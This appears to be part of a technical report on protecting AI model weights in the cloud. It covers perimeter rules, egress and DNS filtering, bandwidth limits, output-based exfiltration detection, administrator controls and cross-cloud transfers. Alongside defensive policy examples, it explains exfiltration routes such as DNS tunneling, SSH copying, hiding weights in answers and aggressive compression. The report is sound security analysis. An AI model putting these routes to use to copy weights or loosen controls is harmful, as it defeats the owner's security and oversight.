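AWS Marketplace, where companies sell software to other AWS customers, lets buyers use a model without letting them copy it. According to AWS's *Security and intellectual property*, a seller's model runs in the buyer's account without network access, and the buyer can't download the container image or the model files. The testing partner could use the company's model this way, but the weights would be in an outside account, and only AWS's controls would keep the partner from reading them.

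### Deciding whether a platform may touch the weights

The company should let a platform use the checkpoint only if the answer to every question is yes:

1. Can the company list every place where the platform keeps a copy, and delete each one?
2. Does the job run under an identity that can reach only the files it needs?
3. Is the job's code cut off from the internet and from storage that outsiders control?
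4. If the person starting the job leaves out a safety setting, do the weights stay protected?
5. Do the perimeter's rules check every call that exports, copies or shares the model?
6. Do the company's own logs show who read each copy?

Suppose the researcher wants to fine-tune the 1 TB checkpoint on Vertex AI. The job runs in project 102 under a custom account called `tuner`, which can read the checkpoint and write to one output bucket in project 101. The job saves its progress twice before it finishes. She then registers the result and deploys it for testing.

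| Step | New copy | Size | Who can read it |
|---|---|---|---|
| The job loads the checkpoint | Google-run training machines | 1 TB | Her code, running as `tuner` |
| The job saves its progress twice | Output bucket | At least 1 TB each time | `tuner` and anyone with access to the bucket |
| The job saves the final weights | Output bucket | 1 TB | The same |
| She registers the model | Google-managed bucket | 1 TB | The serving identity, and anyone who may export the model |
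| She deploys it for testing | Google-run serving machines | 1 TB for each running copy of the model | The code in the serving container |

The company began with one stored copy and now has five, not counting those on running machines. Under RAND's SL3 rule, each of the four new copies needs approval and counts toward the limit. The company can delete the two progress checkpoints as soon as the job ends. Some fine-tuning methods avoid most of this copying by training a small add-on and leaving the original weights unchanged. The add-on is useless without the original, so leaking it matters much less.

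Vertex AI sets the variable `AIP_MODEL_DIR` to the location where the training script should save the model, according to a reply in the Google developer forum thread *Does anyone know how to make my model trained with Vertex AI*. The researcher's script can ignore the variable and try another destination. However, the perimeter blocks uploads to her personal bucket or the sandbox, uploads to a file-sharing site fail because there is no internet route, and `tuner` has no permission to write to the evaluation buckets.

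The training job passes all six questions if the company logs reads of the output bucket and uses the newer network connection. It passes the fourth because the default identity can't read anything in project 101. Registering the model is harder to justify. Google's service agent needs read access to the output bucket to make its copy, and reads of the Google-managed bucket may not appear in the company's logs. The documentation also conflicts, so the fifth question can't be answered until somebody tests the copy call. The company should therefore allow the job, skip the registry, and serve the new weights from its own machines in project 104. The company will then have to track model versions itself.

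On SageMaker, the same job passes with both network settings enforced, and registering the resulting model doesn't create another copy of the weights. On Azure, the job passes if it saves its output to the weights account and the researcher can't change the workspace's outbound rules. Importing any of these models into Bedrock fails the first question, because the company can't see where AWS keeps the copy.

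## Controlling network traffic from machines that hold decrypted weights

Perimeter rules check only requests to the provider's own services, but a test machine with the weights in memory can connect to any address its network can reach. If the researcher rents a server from a small web host and sends the checkpoint there, no perimeter rule applies. So the company has to control which connections the machines can make and how much data they can send.

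### Removing the routes out

The researcher can run any program on her test machine and may be its administrator, so she could switch off a firewall that runs on it. The controls have to be in the surrounding network, where she has no rights.

The first step is to give the machines no public address, including under IPv6, the newer addressing system, so that outsiders can't connect to them directly. However, many companies run a shared NAT gateway that lets machines without public addresses download updates, and it also allows uploads. Older Azure networks provide a similar route by default. An engineer also has to remove these routes from the weights network.

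The second step is to deny outgoing traffic by default. All three clouds normally start with the opposite setting, which lets a machine send traffic anywhere. For the evaluation network, the rules could be as short as this:

| Order | Destination | Action |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Private routes to storage, keys and logging, on port 443 | Allow |
| 2 | The company's proxy, on its one port | Allow |
| 3 | Everything else, inside or outside the company | Deny and log |

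The last rule blocks the upload to the rented server. It also covers the company's internal addresses, because a link to the sandbox's network would let the researcher send the checkpoint there first. One configuration error can undo these protections. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) reports that AI models under test reached the internet in 2026 because an outside firm's evaluation environment was misconfigured.

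A basic firewall rule checks only addresses and ports, which is too crude to single out most websites. Large content delivery companies serve many unrelated sites from the same addresses, so a rule that allows traffic to one site may allow traffic to thousands.

### The proxy and name lookups

A proxy makes connections for a machine. If a test program needs to reach a license server on the internet, it sends the server's name to the proxy, which connects only if that name is on the company's list. This stops uploads to unlisted sites, even those that share an IP address with a listed one.

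Unless the proxy decrypts traffic, it can't stop uploads to a listed site that accepts them. It can also check only the site name a program gives when it connects, and on some shared hosting services the program can then request a different site inside the encrypted connection. A proxy that decrypts traffic can block uploads and limit the size of each request, but some software doesn't work through it. It also does little to stop someone from hiding data in the web addresses of ordinary downloads, although this is slow because sending 100 GB at 8 kilobytes per address would take 12.5 million requests.

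Ideally, the list for the weights network is empty. If researchers get their packages and models from a mirror inside the company, as described earlier, the machines need no internet access, and the company doesn't need the proxy or the second rule in the table.

Name lookups are an easily forgotten way to copy weights out. When a program looks up a website's address, it asks the cloud provider's resolver, which may pass the question to a server run by the owner of that name. The researcher could register a domain and put pieces of the checkpoint in the names she looks up. The resolver would pass them to her server, so her machine would never contact it directly. On AWS and Google Cloud, ordinary firewall rules don't block lookups sent to the provider's resolver.

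A DNS name can hold about 150 bytes of data, so copying 100 GB out takes roughly 670 million DNS lookups. AWS accepts at most 1,024 lookups a second from each network interface. At that rate the copy would take about 7.5 days, and ten machines could do it in under a day.

An engineer can close this route by setting the resolver to answer only for names on a short list. All three clouds offer this filter. The list should contain the company's own names and the cloud services the machines use, without wildcards that cover other customers' names. The firewall must also block other resolvers, including those that accept encrypted lookups over the ordinary web port. The default denial already does this. A new tool will fail until someone adds the names it needs, often with an error message that doesn't mention lookups.

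Private routes to cloud services let the machines keep reading the weights bucket after the engineer removes their internet access. Google Cloud provides a restricted address range for this, AWS provides VPC endpoints with endpoint policies, and Azure provides private endpoints. The perimeter rules still apply to traffic on these routes, so any gap in the rules could still let weights out. The engineer should set up the routes before blocking all other traffic, or the machines will lose access to their storage.

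### Separate paths for administrators and customers

Cloud firewalls generally track connections, and once they admit an incoming connection, they let the replies out without checking the outbound rules. In the Google Cloud setup described earlier, researchers manage their test machines from laptops. If a researcher logs in over SSH, the usual protocol for this, she can download the checkpoint through the same connection even if the rules deny outbound traffic.

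The company should therefore admit logins only from a gateway it controls. The gateway should block file copying and port forwarding (which carries other traffic inside the login session), record screen output, and limit its rate. The company should apply the same restrictions to the providers' own login services, because these can carry files or forwarded connections unless someone turns those features off.

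The rate limit matters because she can still print the file to her screen as text and have her laptop save it. A limit of 10 kilobits per second allows more than 1,000 characters a second, which is faster than anyone reads, but copying 100 GB at that rate would take about two and a half years. Large tables and graphics will load very slowly, so researchers need a reviewed way to export plots.

Answers to customers should travel by a separate path, through a program outside the weights boundary that receives each query, passes it to the serving machines and returns the answer. The serving machines should accept connections only from this program, which can allow only ordinary text of limited length and log every response. These limits block a raw copy of the weights, but someone who controls the serving software can still hide data in text that looks normal.

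### How long a copy takes

Whatever routes remain, the time a thief needs is the size of the copy divided by the rate at which it leaves. With the size *S* in bytes and the rate *R* in bits per second, the time in seconds is

*T* = 8*S* / *R*.

Copying out the 1 TB checkpoint (8 trillion bits) takes about 13 minutes at 10 gigabits per second, 22 hours at 100 megabits per second, and 93 days at 1 megabit per second. A security team can't reliably investigate an alert and respond in 13 minutes, but it has enough time to do both in 93 days.

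A thief may not need the whole terabyte, though, and may have more than one route. If the smaller copy is a fraction *f* of the original and there are *n* routes, then

*T* = 8*fS* / (*R*₁ + *R*₂ + … + *R*ₙ).

The table applies this to smaller copies of the example model, which has a trillion weights.

| Copy | Size | 10 Gbit/s | 100 Mbit/s | 1 Mbit/s |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Complete checkpoint | 1 TB | 13 minutes | 22 hours | 93 days |
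| 4 bits per weight | 500 GB | 7 minutes | 11 hours | 46 days |
| 1.15 bits per weight | 144 GB | 2 minutes | 3 hours | 13 days |
| A quarter of the 4-bit copy | 125 GB | 100 seconds | 3 hours | 12 days |
| 0.1 bits per weight | 12.5 GB | 10 seconds | 17 minutes | 28 hours |

The third and fifth rows use figures from Brown, Rivera and colleagues (2026), in *Aggressive Compression Enables LLM Weight Theft*. They argue that a thief can compress weights much further than a company that has to run the model efficiently, because the thief can retrain the damaged copy afterward. They claim that 16-bit weights can be compressed 16 to 100 times "with minimal trade-offs". The example's weights are one byte each, so the equivalent is 8 to 50 times, which leaves 125 GB to 20 GB.

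The evidence is strongest for the milder compression in that range. A model with 1.5 billion weights, compressed to 1.15 bits each and retrained, scored 54.9% on a test of general knowledge, against 56.5% originally. A model with 7 billion weights did worse, falling from 70.5% to 61.2% at 2.26 bits and to 48.5% at 1.5 bits, although it had much less retraining. The figure of 0.1 bits comes from a 70-billion-weight model and is based on how closely the compressed numbers matched the originals. Brown and colleagues didn't run full evaluations of that model, so the last row of the table is speculative. They also found signs that larger models compress better, which would make a trillion-weight model easier to copy out.

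RAND's planning figure of a tenth, or 100 GB here, still looks reasonable for setting limits. Making the weights harder to compress is a weak alternative. When Brown and colleagues trained a small model to resist compression, it became only 3 to 10% harder to compress.

### Setting a bandwidth limit

The formula can also give the rate limit needed for a chosen detection time. If the company wants at least 30 days to notice a 100 GB copy leaving, the total rate can't exceed about 0.3 megabits per second, or 3.3 GB a day. That may be enough for scores and concise logs from the evaluation environment, but not for verbose debugging logs.

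The limit on outbound traffic has to apply to all routes combined. Fifty test machines, each limited to 1 megabit per second, can together send the full 1 TB checkpoint in 44 hours. Rinberg, Karvonen and colleagues (2025), in *Verifying LLM Inference to Detect Model Weight Exfiltration*, give the extreme case of 10,000 compromised servers that each leak one ten-thousandth of the weights. For this checkpoint, each server would leak 100 MB, which takes 13 minutes at 1 megabit per second.

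The company should enforce the limit at the proxy, the login gateway and the program that handles customers' answers, because an administrator of the test machine can remove a limit set on the machine itself. Logs sent through a private route also need a limit, for instance at a collector that forwards them. Someone also has to investigate when traffic stays near the limit for days, because a daily allowance of 3.3 GB adds up to 1.2 TB in a year, and a patient thief who stays under it can eventually copy all the weights. The company can't assume that the model will have lost much of its value by then.

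### What Anthropic has said about its limits

When Anthropic activated its ASL-3 protections in May 2025, it described its egress bandwidth controls as preliminary and, unlike most of its other new controls, experimental. Because model weights are large, limiting bandwidth makes them slow to copy, which gives security systems time to detect unusual traffic and block it. Anthropic expected that "over time" the limits would become low enough to make it very difficult to copy the weights undetected, even for an attacker who had otherwise compromised its systems. This implies that the limits weren't that low yet. Anthropic also said that it might eventually have to keep weights on networks with no outside connection, and that the limits were a step toward this.

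In the accompanying announcement, Anthropic promised further work on the egress controls and on its protections against more sophisticated insiders. In its February 2026 Risk Report, Anthropic claims only that the limits make large-scale theft of multi-terabyte weights "more time-consuming and detectable". It lists them alongside a control that keeps weights from being written to storage outside its perimeter and another that rejects sensitive operations from unapproved networks. These protections still did not cover sophisticated insiders, a class that includes the researcher.

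*Anthropic's August 2026 Risk Report* (2026), a post on the personal blog ai.rud.is, says the August 2026 edition still listed the limits among ten controls. Anthropic redacted caveats on six of the ten without saying which six. Its 2025 and February 2026 descriptions of the limits give no rate, so an outsider can't calculate whether a copy would take hours or months.

### Why serving needs more capacity

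An evaluation environment can manage with a few gigabytes a day, but a serving cluster has to send answers to customers. Rinberg and colleagues (2025) say providers often have to let hundreds of gigabytes a day in and out of their data centers. Their main example is a 1 TB model with enough traffic to carry a full copy in about a day, or about 93 megabits per second on average. (The paper gives the traffic as "1000Gb", but the one-day figure works only if that means gigabytes.) A limit set just above normal traffic would let a thief take about one copy a day if the thief could use all the allowed traffic. But customers would notice if they stopped getting answers, so the thief has to hide the weights inside the answers.

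Brown and colleagues estimate how much data a thief could hide in output sent to customers. They assume up to 200,000 fake customer accounts, each receiving ten pages of text a day, with a tenth of the data carrying hidden content. That comes to 600 MB a day, so copying 100 GB would take 167 days. If each account also receives one image a day, the total rises to about 31 GB a day, and the same copy would take just over three days. They suggest keeping image and voice generation physically separate from the servers that hold the language model, so that the company can set those servers' outgoing data limit for text alone.

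They assume a fixed probability *p* of catching the thief each day, so a theft lasting *T* days goes undetected with probability (1 − *p*)^*T*. At their value of 0.1% a day, the text-only theft of 100 GB succeeds about 85% of the time. The value of *p* is a guess, and they acknowledge that a busier thief should be easier to detect, which the model leaves out. Still, the model shows that a bandwidth limit does little good if nobody monitors the traffic.

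The company could also lower the limit by compressing the answers before they leave the boundary. In *Haiku to Opus in Just 10 bits*, Rinberg, Carrell and colleagues (2026) compressed conversations with AI models to about a tenth of their original size, without losing any text, by using another language model to predict the text. If the example's traffic compressed by the same ratio, the limit could fall from 1 TB to about 100 GB a day.

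In a more drastic design, a small model outside the boundary writes the answer, and the protected model only answers ten yes-or-no questions about it. Depending on the test, this fixed between 7% and 72% of the problems that the small model had got wrong and the protected model could solve. On the easier tests, though, the small model did nearly as well when it answered its own questions, so most of the gain there didn't come from the protected model. Neither method is ready for ordinary customers. The lossless method fails if the machines at each end calculate slightly different probabilities, which happens often on current hardware, and nobody has tested the question method on open-ended writing.

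### Detecting weights hidden in answers

A language model generates text one token (a word or part of a word) at a time, selecting each partly at random from likely candidates. The random numbers come from a starting value called a seed. If a trusted server runs the same prompt with the same seed, it should produce the same tokens, so a thief who changes tokens to carry data will cause mismatches. The trusted server belongs inside the boundary because it needs its own copy of the weights, and that copy must also be protected.

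Rinberg and colleagues (2025) used this method on a model with 30 billion weights and cut the share of traffic that could carry hidden stolen data to below 0.5%. In their 1 TB example, this lengthens the theft from one day to more than 200. At the same share, stealing a 100 GB copy would take only about 20 days. The paper reports its false alarm rate as 1% in one place and 0.01% in another.

In a follow-up study, *Anytime-valid detection of LLM weight exfiltration*, Ortega-Fernandez, Kowalczyk and Warr (2026) found that false alarms were a serious problem. Honest servers don't reproduce each other's tokens exactly, because small rounding differences can change which token is chosen when two score almost equally. Across the four models tested, 41% to 87% of honest responses contained at least one mismatch. They then turned the 2025 method into an alarm that sounds at the first token it classes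 as dangerous. Over 250 responses, it went off for at least 98% of honest streams and missed the simpler of two attacks entirely. The 2025 paper didn't specify how to combine results over time, so this tests only one way of using its method.

Their own method adds up evidence across responses. It starts at 1 and multiplies the evidence after each response by

1 + λ(*A* − *q*).

Here *A* is 1 if the response contains a mismatch too large to explain easily by rounding, and 0 otherwise. The number *q* is a cautious estimate of how often honest responses contain such a mismatch, and λ sets how much each response changes the evidence. If *q* is 0.1 and λ is 2, a response with such a mismatch multiplies the evidence by 2.8, and one without multiplies it by 0.8. The full method averages seven such products, each with a different definition of "too large", and raises an alarm when the average reaches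 200. On honest traffic the evidence doesn't grow on average, so it has at most a 1 in 200 chance of ever reaching 200. Allowing another 0.5% for a bad estimate of *q*, the chance of a false alarm is at most 1%, however long the monitoring runs.

That guarantee holds only while the prompts, model and serving software stay similar to those used for calibration. Customers' prompts change constantly, so a company would have to recalibrate regularly.

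The method caught the simpler attack in every simulated stream, typically after 6 to 14 responses. A thief who can reconstruct the random choices is harder to catch, because he can limit his changes to tokens that rounding might have changed anyway. On a 32-billion-weight model, the method caught such a thief after a median of 85 responses when he hid about 0.026 bits per token. On a 30-billion-weight model of a different design, it never caught him within 250 responses, even when he hid 0.03 bits per token.

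At 0.03 bits per token, copying 100 GB of weights would take about 26 trillion tokens. If a token is about four bytes of text, a cluster that sends 1 TB of text a day would need around 105 days to produce them, and the thief would have to control all of its output. That is slow enough for bandwidth limits and ordinary monitoring to matter. A 256-bit encryption key, however, would fit in about 8,500 tokens, or a few long answers. A thief who already had an encrypted copy of the weights would need only the key, so the serving software shouldn't be able to read it, even if the provider releases it only to verified machines.

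## Protecting the perimeter rules from administrators

The perimeter consists of settings that somebody at the company can change. If the researcher can edit the weights perimeter on Google Cloud, she can add an egress rule for project 901, copy the checkpoint and then delete the rule. The perimeter is then discretionary for her, even if it is mandatory for her colleagues.

The company needs a list of everyone who can read the weights and another of everyone who can change the perimeter rules, and no one should be on both. The second list is harder to write because it has to include anyone who could gain that ability, such as a help-desk employee who can reset an administrator's password or an engineer who can alter the program that applies the rules.

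### Who can weaken the rules

| Cloud | Who | What they can do | What restrains them |
|---|---|---|---|
| Google Cloud | Access policy administrators and editors | Change perimeters and their ingress and egress rules | The perimeter, until they change it |
| Google Cloud | Organization administrators | Give themselves the access policy role | The same |
| AWS | Administrators in the management account | Change, detach or switch off SCPs and RCPs | No SCP; RCPs on other accounts, until they change them |
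| AWS | Delegated administrators | Change the policies that the management account lets them manage | SCPs and RCPs |
| AWS | Administrators of any other account | Take the account out of the organization, unless an SCP forbids it | SCPs and RCPs, until the account leaves |
| Azure | Global administrators | Give themselves any role in every subscription in the tenant | Azure Policy, until they change it |
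| Azure | Subscription owners | Change storage and network settings, or move the subscription to another tenant | Policies assigned above the subscription |

On Google Cloud, super administrators, who manage the company's user accounts, can appoint organization administrators. If a perimeter includes a whole folder, anyone who can move a project out of that folder can take that project out of the perimeter.

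SCPs have no effect on users and roles in an AWS organization's management account, according to AWS's *Service control policies (SCPs)*, and AWS says that RCPs don't protect resources in that account. An administrator there can also switch off SCPs for the whole organization, which detaches them all. Switching SCPs back on doesn't restore the attachments, so someone has to reattach each policy by hand.

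Other accounts can escape by leaving. AWS's *CIRT insights*, a post by the company's incident response team, reports that attackers who gain control of an account have started removing it from its organization. The organization's SCPs then stop applying, and its central log stops recording what happens in the account. If an administrator did this to account 111111111111, he could share the weights bucket with anyone. This SCP statement prevents it:

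```json
{
  "Sid": "NoLeaving",
  "Effect": "Deny",
  "Action": [
    "organizations:LeaveOrganization",
    "organizations:AcceptHandshake",
    "account:CloseAccount"
  ],
  "Resource": "*"
}
```

AWS now attaches a similar SCP by default, but only to organizations that customers create in its web console after July 10, 2026. Customers can still modify this default SCP, and it leaves out `AcceptHandshake`, the call that accepts an invitation to join another organization. Because SCPs don't apply to the management account, that account can still remove a member account.

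AWS's *Managed policies for your organization* describes a stricter arrangement that AWS is releasing to a limited number of customers. AWS manages the SCPs itself, and customers can't change the one that blocks accounts from leaving the organization, so it binds even their top administrators. But that SCP covers only departures and AWS's own management roles, so it doesn't stop anyone from copying weights to an outside bucket.

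On Azure, global administrators have no automatic access to storage, but they can turn on a setting that lets them assign roles in every subscription. Any global administrator of the weights tenant could therefore gain access to the weights. Subscription owners have less power over policies. Exempting a resource from a rule requires rights over both the resource and the rule's assignment, so an owner normally can't waive a rule that the company assigned above the subscription level. The company should turn on the tenant setting that stops subscriptions from being moved to another tenant.

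### Keeping weights and readers away from the top

The first protection is to keep the weights out of the management account. AWS's *Best practices for the management account* recommends storing all resources in other accounts and using the management account only for tasks that require it. It also recommends reviewing every month or quarter who has access to the account's email address, password, second factor and phone number. Someone who controls the mailbox and phone may be able to reset the password of the root user, the account's most powerful identity.

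Root users in other accounts are less dangerous because SCPs do apply to them. The company can also remove their credentials centrally, which AWS says prevents anyone from recovering them.

Google Cloud has no equivalent account that needs to be emptied, because every bucket belongs to an ordinary project. On Azure, the dedicated weights tenant keeps the main company's global administrators away from the weights, provided different people administer that tenant.

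Next, the company should separate the people who may read the weights from those who edit the perimeter rules. On AWS, it can do this by delegating policy management to an account used for nothing else. Tenable, a security vendor, recommends this for both SCPs and RCPs in its check *2.1.5 Ensure delegated admin manages AWS Organizations policies*. Fewer people then need the management account, and SCPs apply to the people who edit the policies. The company creates the delegation from the management account and can give different accounts different powers, so it should withhold the power to switch off all SCPs.

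The separation makes troubleshooting slower. When a researcher can't open the checkpoint, the person who fixes the rule can't open it either, so the company should keep a harmless file in the same bucket for testing the fix.

### Changing rules through reviewed code

The company should store every rule as a text file and let only one program, the deployment pipeline, apply changes. The sample project *scp management reference architecture* does this for SCPs. It has a folder for each organizational unit and uses Terraform, a tool that configures cloud resources from files. An engineer proposes an edit, reviewers see which lines would change, and the pipeline applies the approved version.

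An SCP on the policy account can deny policy edits to every identity except the pipeline's. The delegation should exclude that SCP, so that only the management account can change it. The management account can still edit the rules directly, so the pipeline should compare the live rules with the files every few minutes to catch such edits.

Requiring review shifts some control over the perimeter to the people who run the pipeline. Anyone who can change the pipeline's code, log in to its machine or switch off the review requirement can change the perimeter. The company should list these people among the perimeter's editors and put the pipeline's own settings under the same review.

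### Requiring a second person, for a limited time

AWS's Multi-party approval feature looks like the obvious way to protect the rules. A company names a team of approvers and sets how many must agree. According to AWS's *Terms and concepts for Multi-party approval*, a request stays open for 24 hours, and no response counts as a rejection. Once enough approvers agree, AWS automatically carries out the operation with the requester's permissions. Changing an active team also requires the team's approval, so an administrator can't replace the approvers without it.

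AWS's multi-party approval doesn't cover perimeter rules. In late May 2026, AWS's *What is Multi-party approval?* listed protected operations only for AWS Backup and Payment Cryptography, a service for handling payment keys. It didn't list edits to SCPs or RCPs. The list may grow, since AWS (2026) had added Payment Cryptography only in April.

The feature can still protect against one way of copying weights. If the company keeps a backup of the checkpoint in one of AWS's isolated vaults, it can require approval before another account gets access to restore the backup.

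An approval system can be defeated if administrators of the sign-in system reset an approver's credentials and vote in that person's place. To prevent this, AWS has required approvers since February to enter a six-digit code from their email when they vote (AWS, 2026). The codes help only if the same administrators don't also control the approvers' mailboxes.

With Google's Privileged Access Manager and Microsoft's Privileged Identity Management, a person requests a role, an approver agrees, and the role expires after a set time. This suits access policy administrators and global administrators, who shouldn't hold those roles permanently. But the approver approves the role without seeing which rules the person will then change.

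It is technically possible for a provider to require approval for rule changes too. Snowflake's *Multi-party Approval (General availability)* (2026) describes a feature of the company's data platform that can require a second administrator to approve changes to network policies, grants of administrative roles and the approval settings themselves.

| Method | What the second person approves | Does it cover perimeter rules? |
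|---|---|---|
| AWS Multi-party approval | One operation on a backup vault or payment key | No |
| Google Privileged Access Manager | A role for a limited time | Yes, but not each edit |
| Microsoft Privileged Identity Management | A role for a limited time | Yes, but not each edit |
| Reviewed code | The exact text of the change | Yes, unless someone edits the rules directly |

The company should make ordinary changes through a pipeline that deploys reviewed code, and grant time-limited roles for the few tasks that the pipeline can't do. On AWS, it has to build or buy the approval step for those roles.

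### Guarding the tags that exceptions rely on

Some of the AWS rules described earlier exempt identities with a certain tag, such as `dp:exclude:network`, and others apply only to tagged identities. Anyone who can add or remove these tags can therefore weaken the perimeter without editing a policy. This SCP statement reserves both powers for one group:

```json
{
  "Sid": "ProtectExceptionTags",
  "Effect": "Deny",
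  "Action": [
    "iam:CreateRole", "iam:TagRole", "iam:UntagRole",
    "iam:CreateUser", "iam:TagUser", "iam:UntagUser",
    "sts:TagSession"
  ],
  "Resource": "*",
  "Condition": {
    "ForAnyValue:StringLike": { "aws:TagKeys": ["dp:*", "team"] },
    "StringNotEqualsIfExists": { "aws:PrincipalTag/team": "admin" }
  }
}
```

The statement follows the approach in *data perimeter policy examples*, a copy of AWS's published samples, where only identities with the tag `team` set to `admin` may change the exception tags. It must also restrict changes to the `team` tag, or a researcher could set her own to `admin` and then change the exception tags.

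`sts:TagSession` covers tags that last for a single login. The samples also include an RCP that restricts these tags, except when they come from the company's own sign-in system. Whoever runs that system can therefore grant exemptions and belongs on the list of editors. The company should also deny `iam:CreateSAMLProvider` and `iam:UpdateSAMLProvider`, so that nobody can connect their own sign-in system.

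Exemptions for named roles need the same care. AWS's *Perimeter implementation* suggests exempting a privileged role, if necessary, from the ban on sharing snapshots and images. Everyone who can use that role can then share a disk that contains the weights.

On Google Cloud, the people to watch are those who manage any groups named in ingress and egress rules.

### Alerting from a separate account

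Each cloud records changes to its rules, and the company should copy those records to a logging account that neither readers nor rule editors can alter. Every change should alert someone outside both groups, who checks that it matches an approved edit. On AWS, the alerts should cover policy edits, new delegations and any account that leaves the organization. In May, AWS added log events for departures, which made them easier to detect (AWS, 2026).

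The logging account needs protection too. AWS's *Mandatory controls* lists SCPs that Control Tower applies to its security accounts, including one that blocks changes to the encryption of the log buckets. An administrator in the management account could remove these SCPs, so removing any of them should trigger an immediate alert, before the administrator has time to interfere with the logs.

### An emergency procedure

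Suppose that at 2 a.m. on a Saturday, a faulty SCP stops the serving machines from reading the checkpoint. The same SCP blocks the pipeline, so nobody can fix it in the normal way. The company needs a role in the management account for this, because a faulty SCP can't lock that role out. The procedure could work like this:

1. The on-call engineer, who can't read the weights, asks for the emergency role and names the policy she needs to change.
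2. Two of five approvers phone her to confirm the request and then approve it with their own security keys. None of the five works on her team or can read the weights. If two haven't approved within 15 minutes, the request fails and she has to start again.
3. She gets credentials that expire after 60 minutes. They let her change SCPs and RCPs, but not read buckets, remove accounts, switch off a policy type, edit the role's own permissions or change logging.
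4. She first attaches a prepared SCP that stops everyone except the serving machines from reading the weights.
5. She restores the last reviewed version of the faulty SCP while one of the approvers watches her screen.
6. By the end of the next working day, two people who weren't involved compare the live rules with the files and check who read the weights. They then restore the researchers' access.

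The fourth step is needed because a time limit alone wouldn't protect the checkpoint. A direct copy between two buckets doesn't cross the company's network, so the bandwidth limits don't slow it, and someone could copy out a terabyte well within the hour. The drawback is that researchers can't use the weights until somebody finishes the review.

| Evidence | What it shows |
|---|---|
| The request and the approvers' answers, with times | Who agreed to the access, and why |
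| AWS's log of calls made with the emergency role | Everything the engineer did |
| The policies before and after | Whether she changed only what she had named |
| The log of reads from the weights bucket | Whether anyone took advantage of the change |
| The reviewers' findings | Whether the rules returned to normal |

The approval records need to be stored permanently. AWS says its approval portal, for example, shows past decisions for at most one month.

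A larger approval team makes the procedure more likely to work at night. If each approver has a 70% chance of answering in time, the chance that at least two answer is about 97% for a team of five and 78% for a team of three. Approvers also change jobs or stop reading their messages. Since March, AWS has let customers run test approvals to find unresponsive approvers in advance (*Multi-party approval now supports approval team baselining* (2026)), and the company should run similar drills with its own tool.

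### Two administrators who work together

Two dishonest administrators can defeat the ordinary review. One proposes an exception for the researcher's account (999999999999), the other approves it, and the pipeline applies it.

The usual reply is that collusion is much rarer than a single dishonest employee. If each of *n* administrators would help a thief with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance that at least two would help is

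1 − (1 − *p*)^*n* − *np*(1 − *p*)^(*n* − 1).

If each of six administrators independently had a 1% chance of being willing to help, a made-up figure, the chance that at least one would help is 5.9%. The chance that at least two would is 0.15%, about 40 times lower. The two would also have to find each other, and one who approaches an honest colleague may be reported to security.

The independence assumption is doubtful, though, because a recruiter who has bribed one administrator can ask which colleague is in debt, and a thief who steals two sets of credentials needs no willing accomplice. Careless approvers may be the bigger problem. If they approve one request in five without reading it, a lone insider has a 20% chance of getting a harmful rule approved on each attempt. The pipeline can reduce this risk by checking whether a proposed rule would allow a copy to an outside account and rejecting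 it unless the destination is on a separate list.

Detection is also less useful for weights than for most things, because the company can't get a stolen copy back. An alert an hour after the theft may still identify the thieves, which deters some people. The company should therefore wait 24 hours after approving any change that loosens the perimeter before applying it, and send the alert at the start of the wait. The two administrators would then also need whoever receives the alerts to stay silent. Changes that tighten the rules can take effect at once. Partners will sometimes have to wait a day for an exception, and real emergencies go through the three-person procedure above.

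With the delay in place, I expect the perimeter to hold against one dishonest administrator and to have a fair chance against two. It doesn't hold against someone with unrestricted access to the management account, or the equivalent on other clouds, so nobody should have that access alone. None of these controls restrict the cloud provider's own staff.

### What Anthropic says it does

Anthropic reported in May 2025 that it had automated its two-person rule for temporary access to weights. It says this makes a single compromised account less likely to expose the weights.

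It also tightened controls on changes to the code repositories that hold weights and security infrastructure. Some changes need additional reviews, engineers must sign their changes cryptographically, and designated teams own the critical files. Claude, Anthropic's model, helps review routine changes, especially to less sensitive files. For perimeter rules, a company should require both reviewers to be human, at least until it has evidence that a model reliably detects harmful exceptions.

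Anthropic's list of further work included "resolving and reducing exceptions and bypasses to our controls", so some existed at the time. Anthropic didn't publish how many there were or how many people could approve new ones.

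## Moving weights between cloud providers

A company that trains a model on one cloud and serves it on another has to move the weights from one perimeter to another. Google's ownership checks apply to Google Cloud projects, and AWS's apply to AWS accounts. Google Cloud therefore treats the company's own S3 bucket as a third-party internet site, just like the researcher's. (Google's egress rules can name an S3 bucket for BigQuery Omni, a data analysis product, but not for an ordinary upload.) No label travels with the checkpoint either, so once it reaches AWS, only the company's AWS rules protect it.

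At least two leading developers, Anthropic and OpenAI, have to move weights between cloud providers. In October 2025, Anthropic announced that it would use up to a million of Google's AI chips, while still calling Amazon its primary training partner. In November, it and Microsoft announced that Claude would also be available through Azure. OpenAI, long dependent on Azure, announced a $38 billion agreement for AWS capacity the same month. Google is in an easier position because it can train and serve Gemini in its own data centers. These announcements don't show where every copy is, since a cloud can offer a model in its catalog and forward customers' queries to machines elsewhere.

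Suppose the company in the example trains on Google Cloud and serves on AWS. It has to move the 1 TB checkpoint from the bucket in project 101 to a bucket in account 111111111111, where the serving machines can read it.

### A direct copy under a narrow exception

The simplest method is to let one machine on Google Cloud upload the file:

1. An engineer creates an AWS role that can write to the destination bucket but can't read from it.
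2. She lets one Google service account use the role, identified by its unique number. A condition that accepted any Google identity would admit other Google customers. The RCP that protects AWS roles also needs an exception for this identity.
3. She opens the firewall from one machine in project 102 to the destination bucket.
4. She runs the copy, compares the file's hash (a short fingerprint of its contents) at both ends, and closes the firewall.

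The third step is the weak one because S3 buckets share addresses. A rule that allows traffic to those addresses allows traffic to every AWS customer's bucket. Anyone who can run a program on the sending machine could then use personal AWS keys to upload the checkpoint to a personal bucket, and no perimeter rule on either cloud would stop the upload.

S3 lets a caller specify which account should own the destination bucket, and refuses the upload if another account owns it. This check catches mistakes, but a thief can leave it out.

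The company can restore an ownership test by routing the traffic over a private connection between the two clouds. The connection leads to a VPC endpoint in account 111111111111, whose policy accepts only company identities and company buckets. The Google firewall allows only that endpoint's private address. The endpoint then rejects uploads made with personal keys. The bucket's existing network rule refuses downloads through that endpoint.

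The engineer still handles the checkpoint herself, and whoever can edit the firewall can reopen the route to the internet.

### A transfer service that no reader can use

The company can instead have a program move the weights. The program has its own identity and runs in a new project inside the weights perimeter. Researchers can't log in to its machine, use its identity or change its code.

1. Someone requests a transfer by giving the checkpoint's hash. The request has no field for a destination, because the reviewed code contains the only one.
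2. Two people who can't read the weights approve the request.
3. The program reads the file, confirms the hash and sends the file through the private connection.
4. A second program on AWS checks the hash again, moves the file to the weights bucket and deletes the temporary copy.

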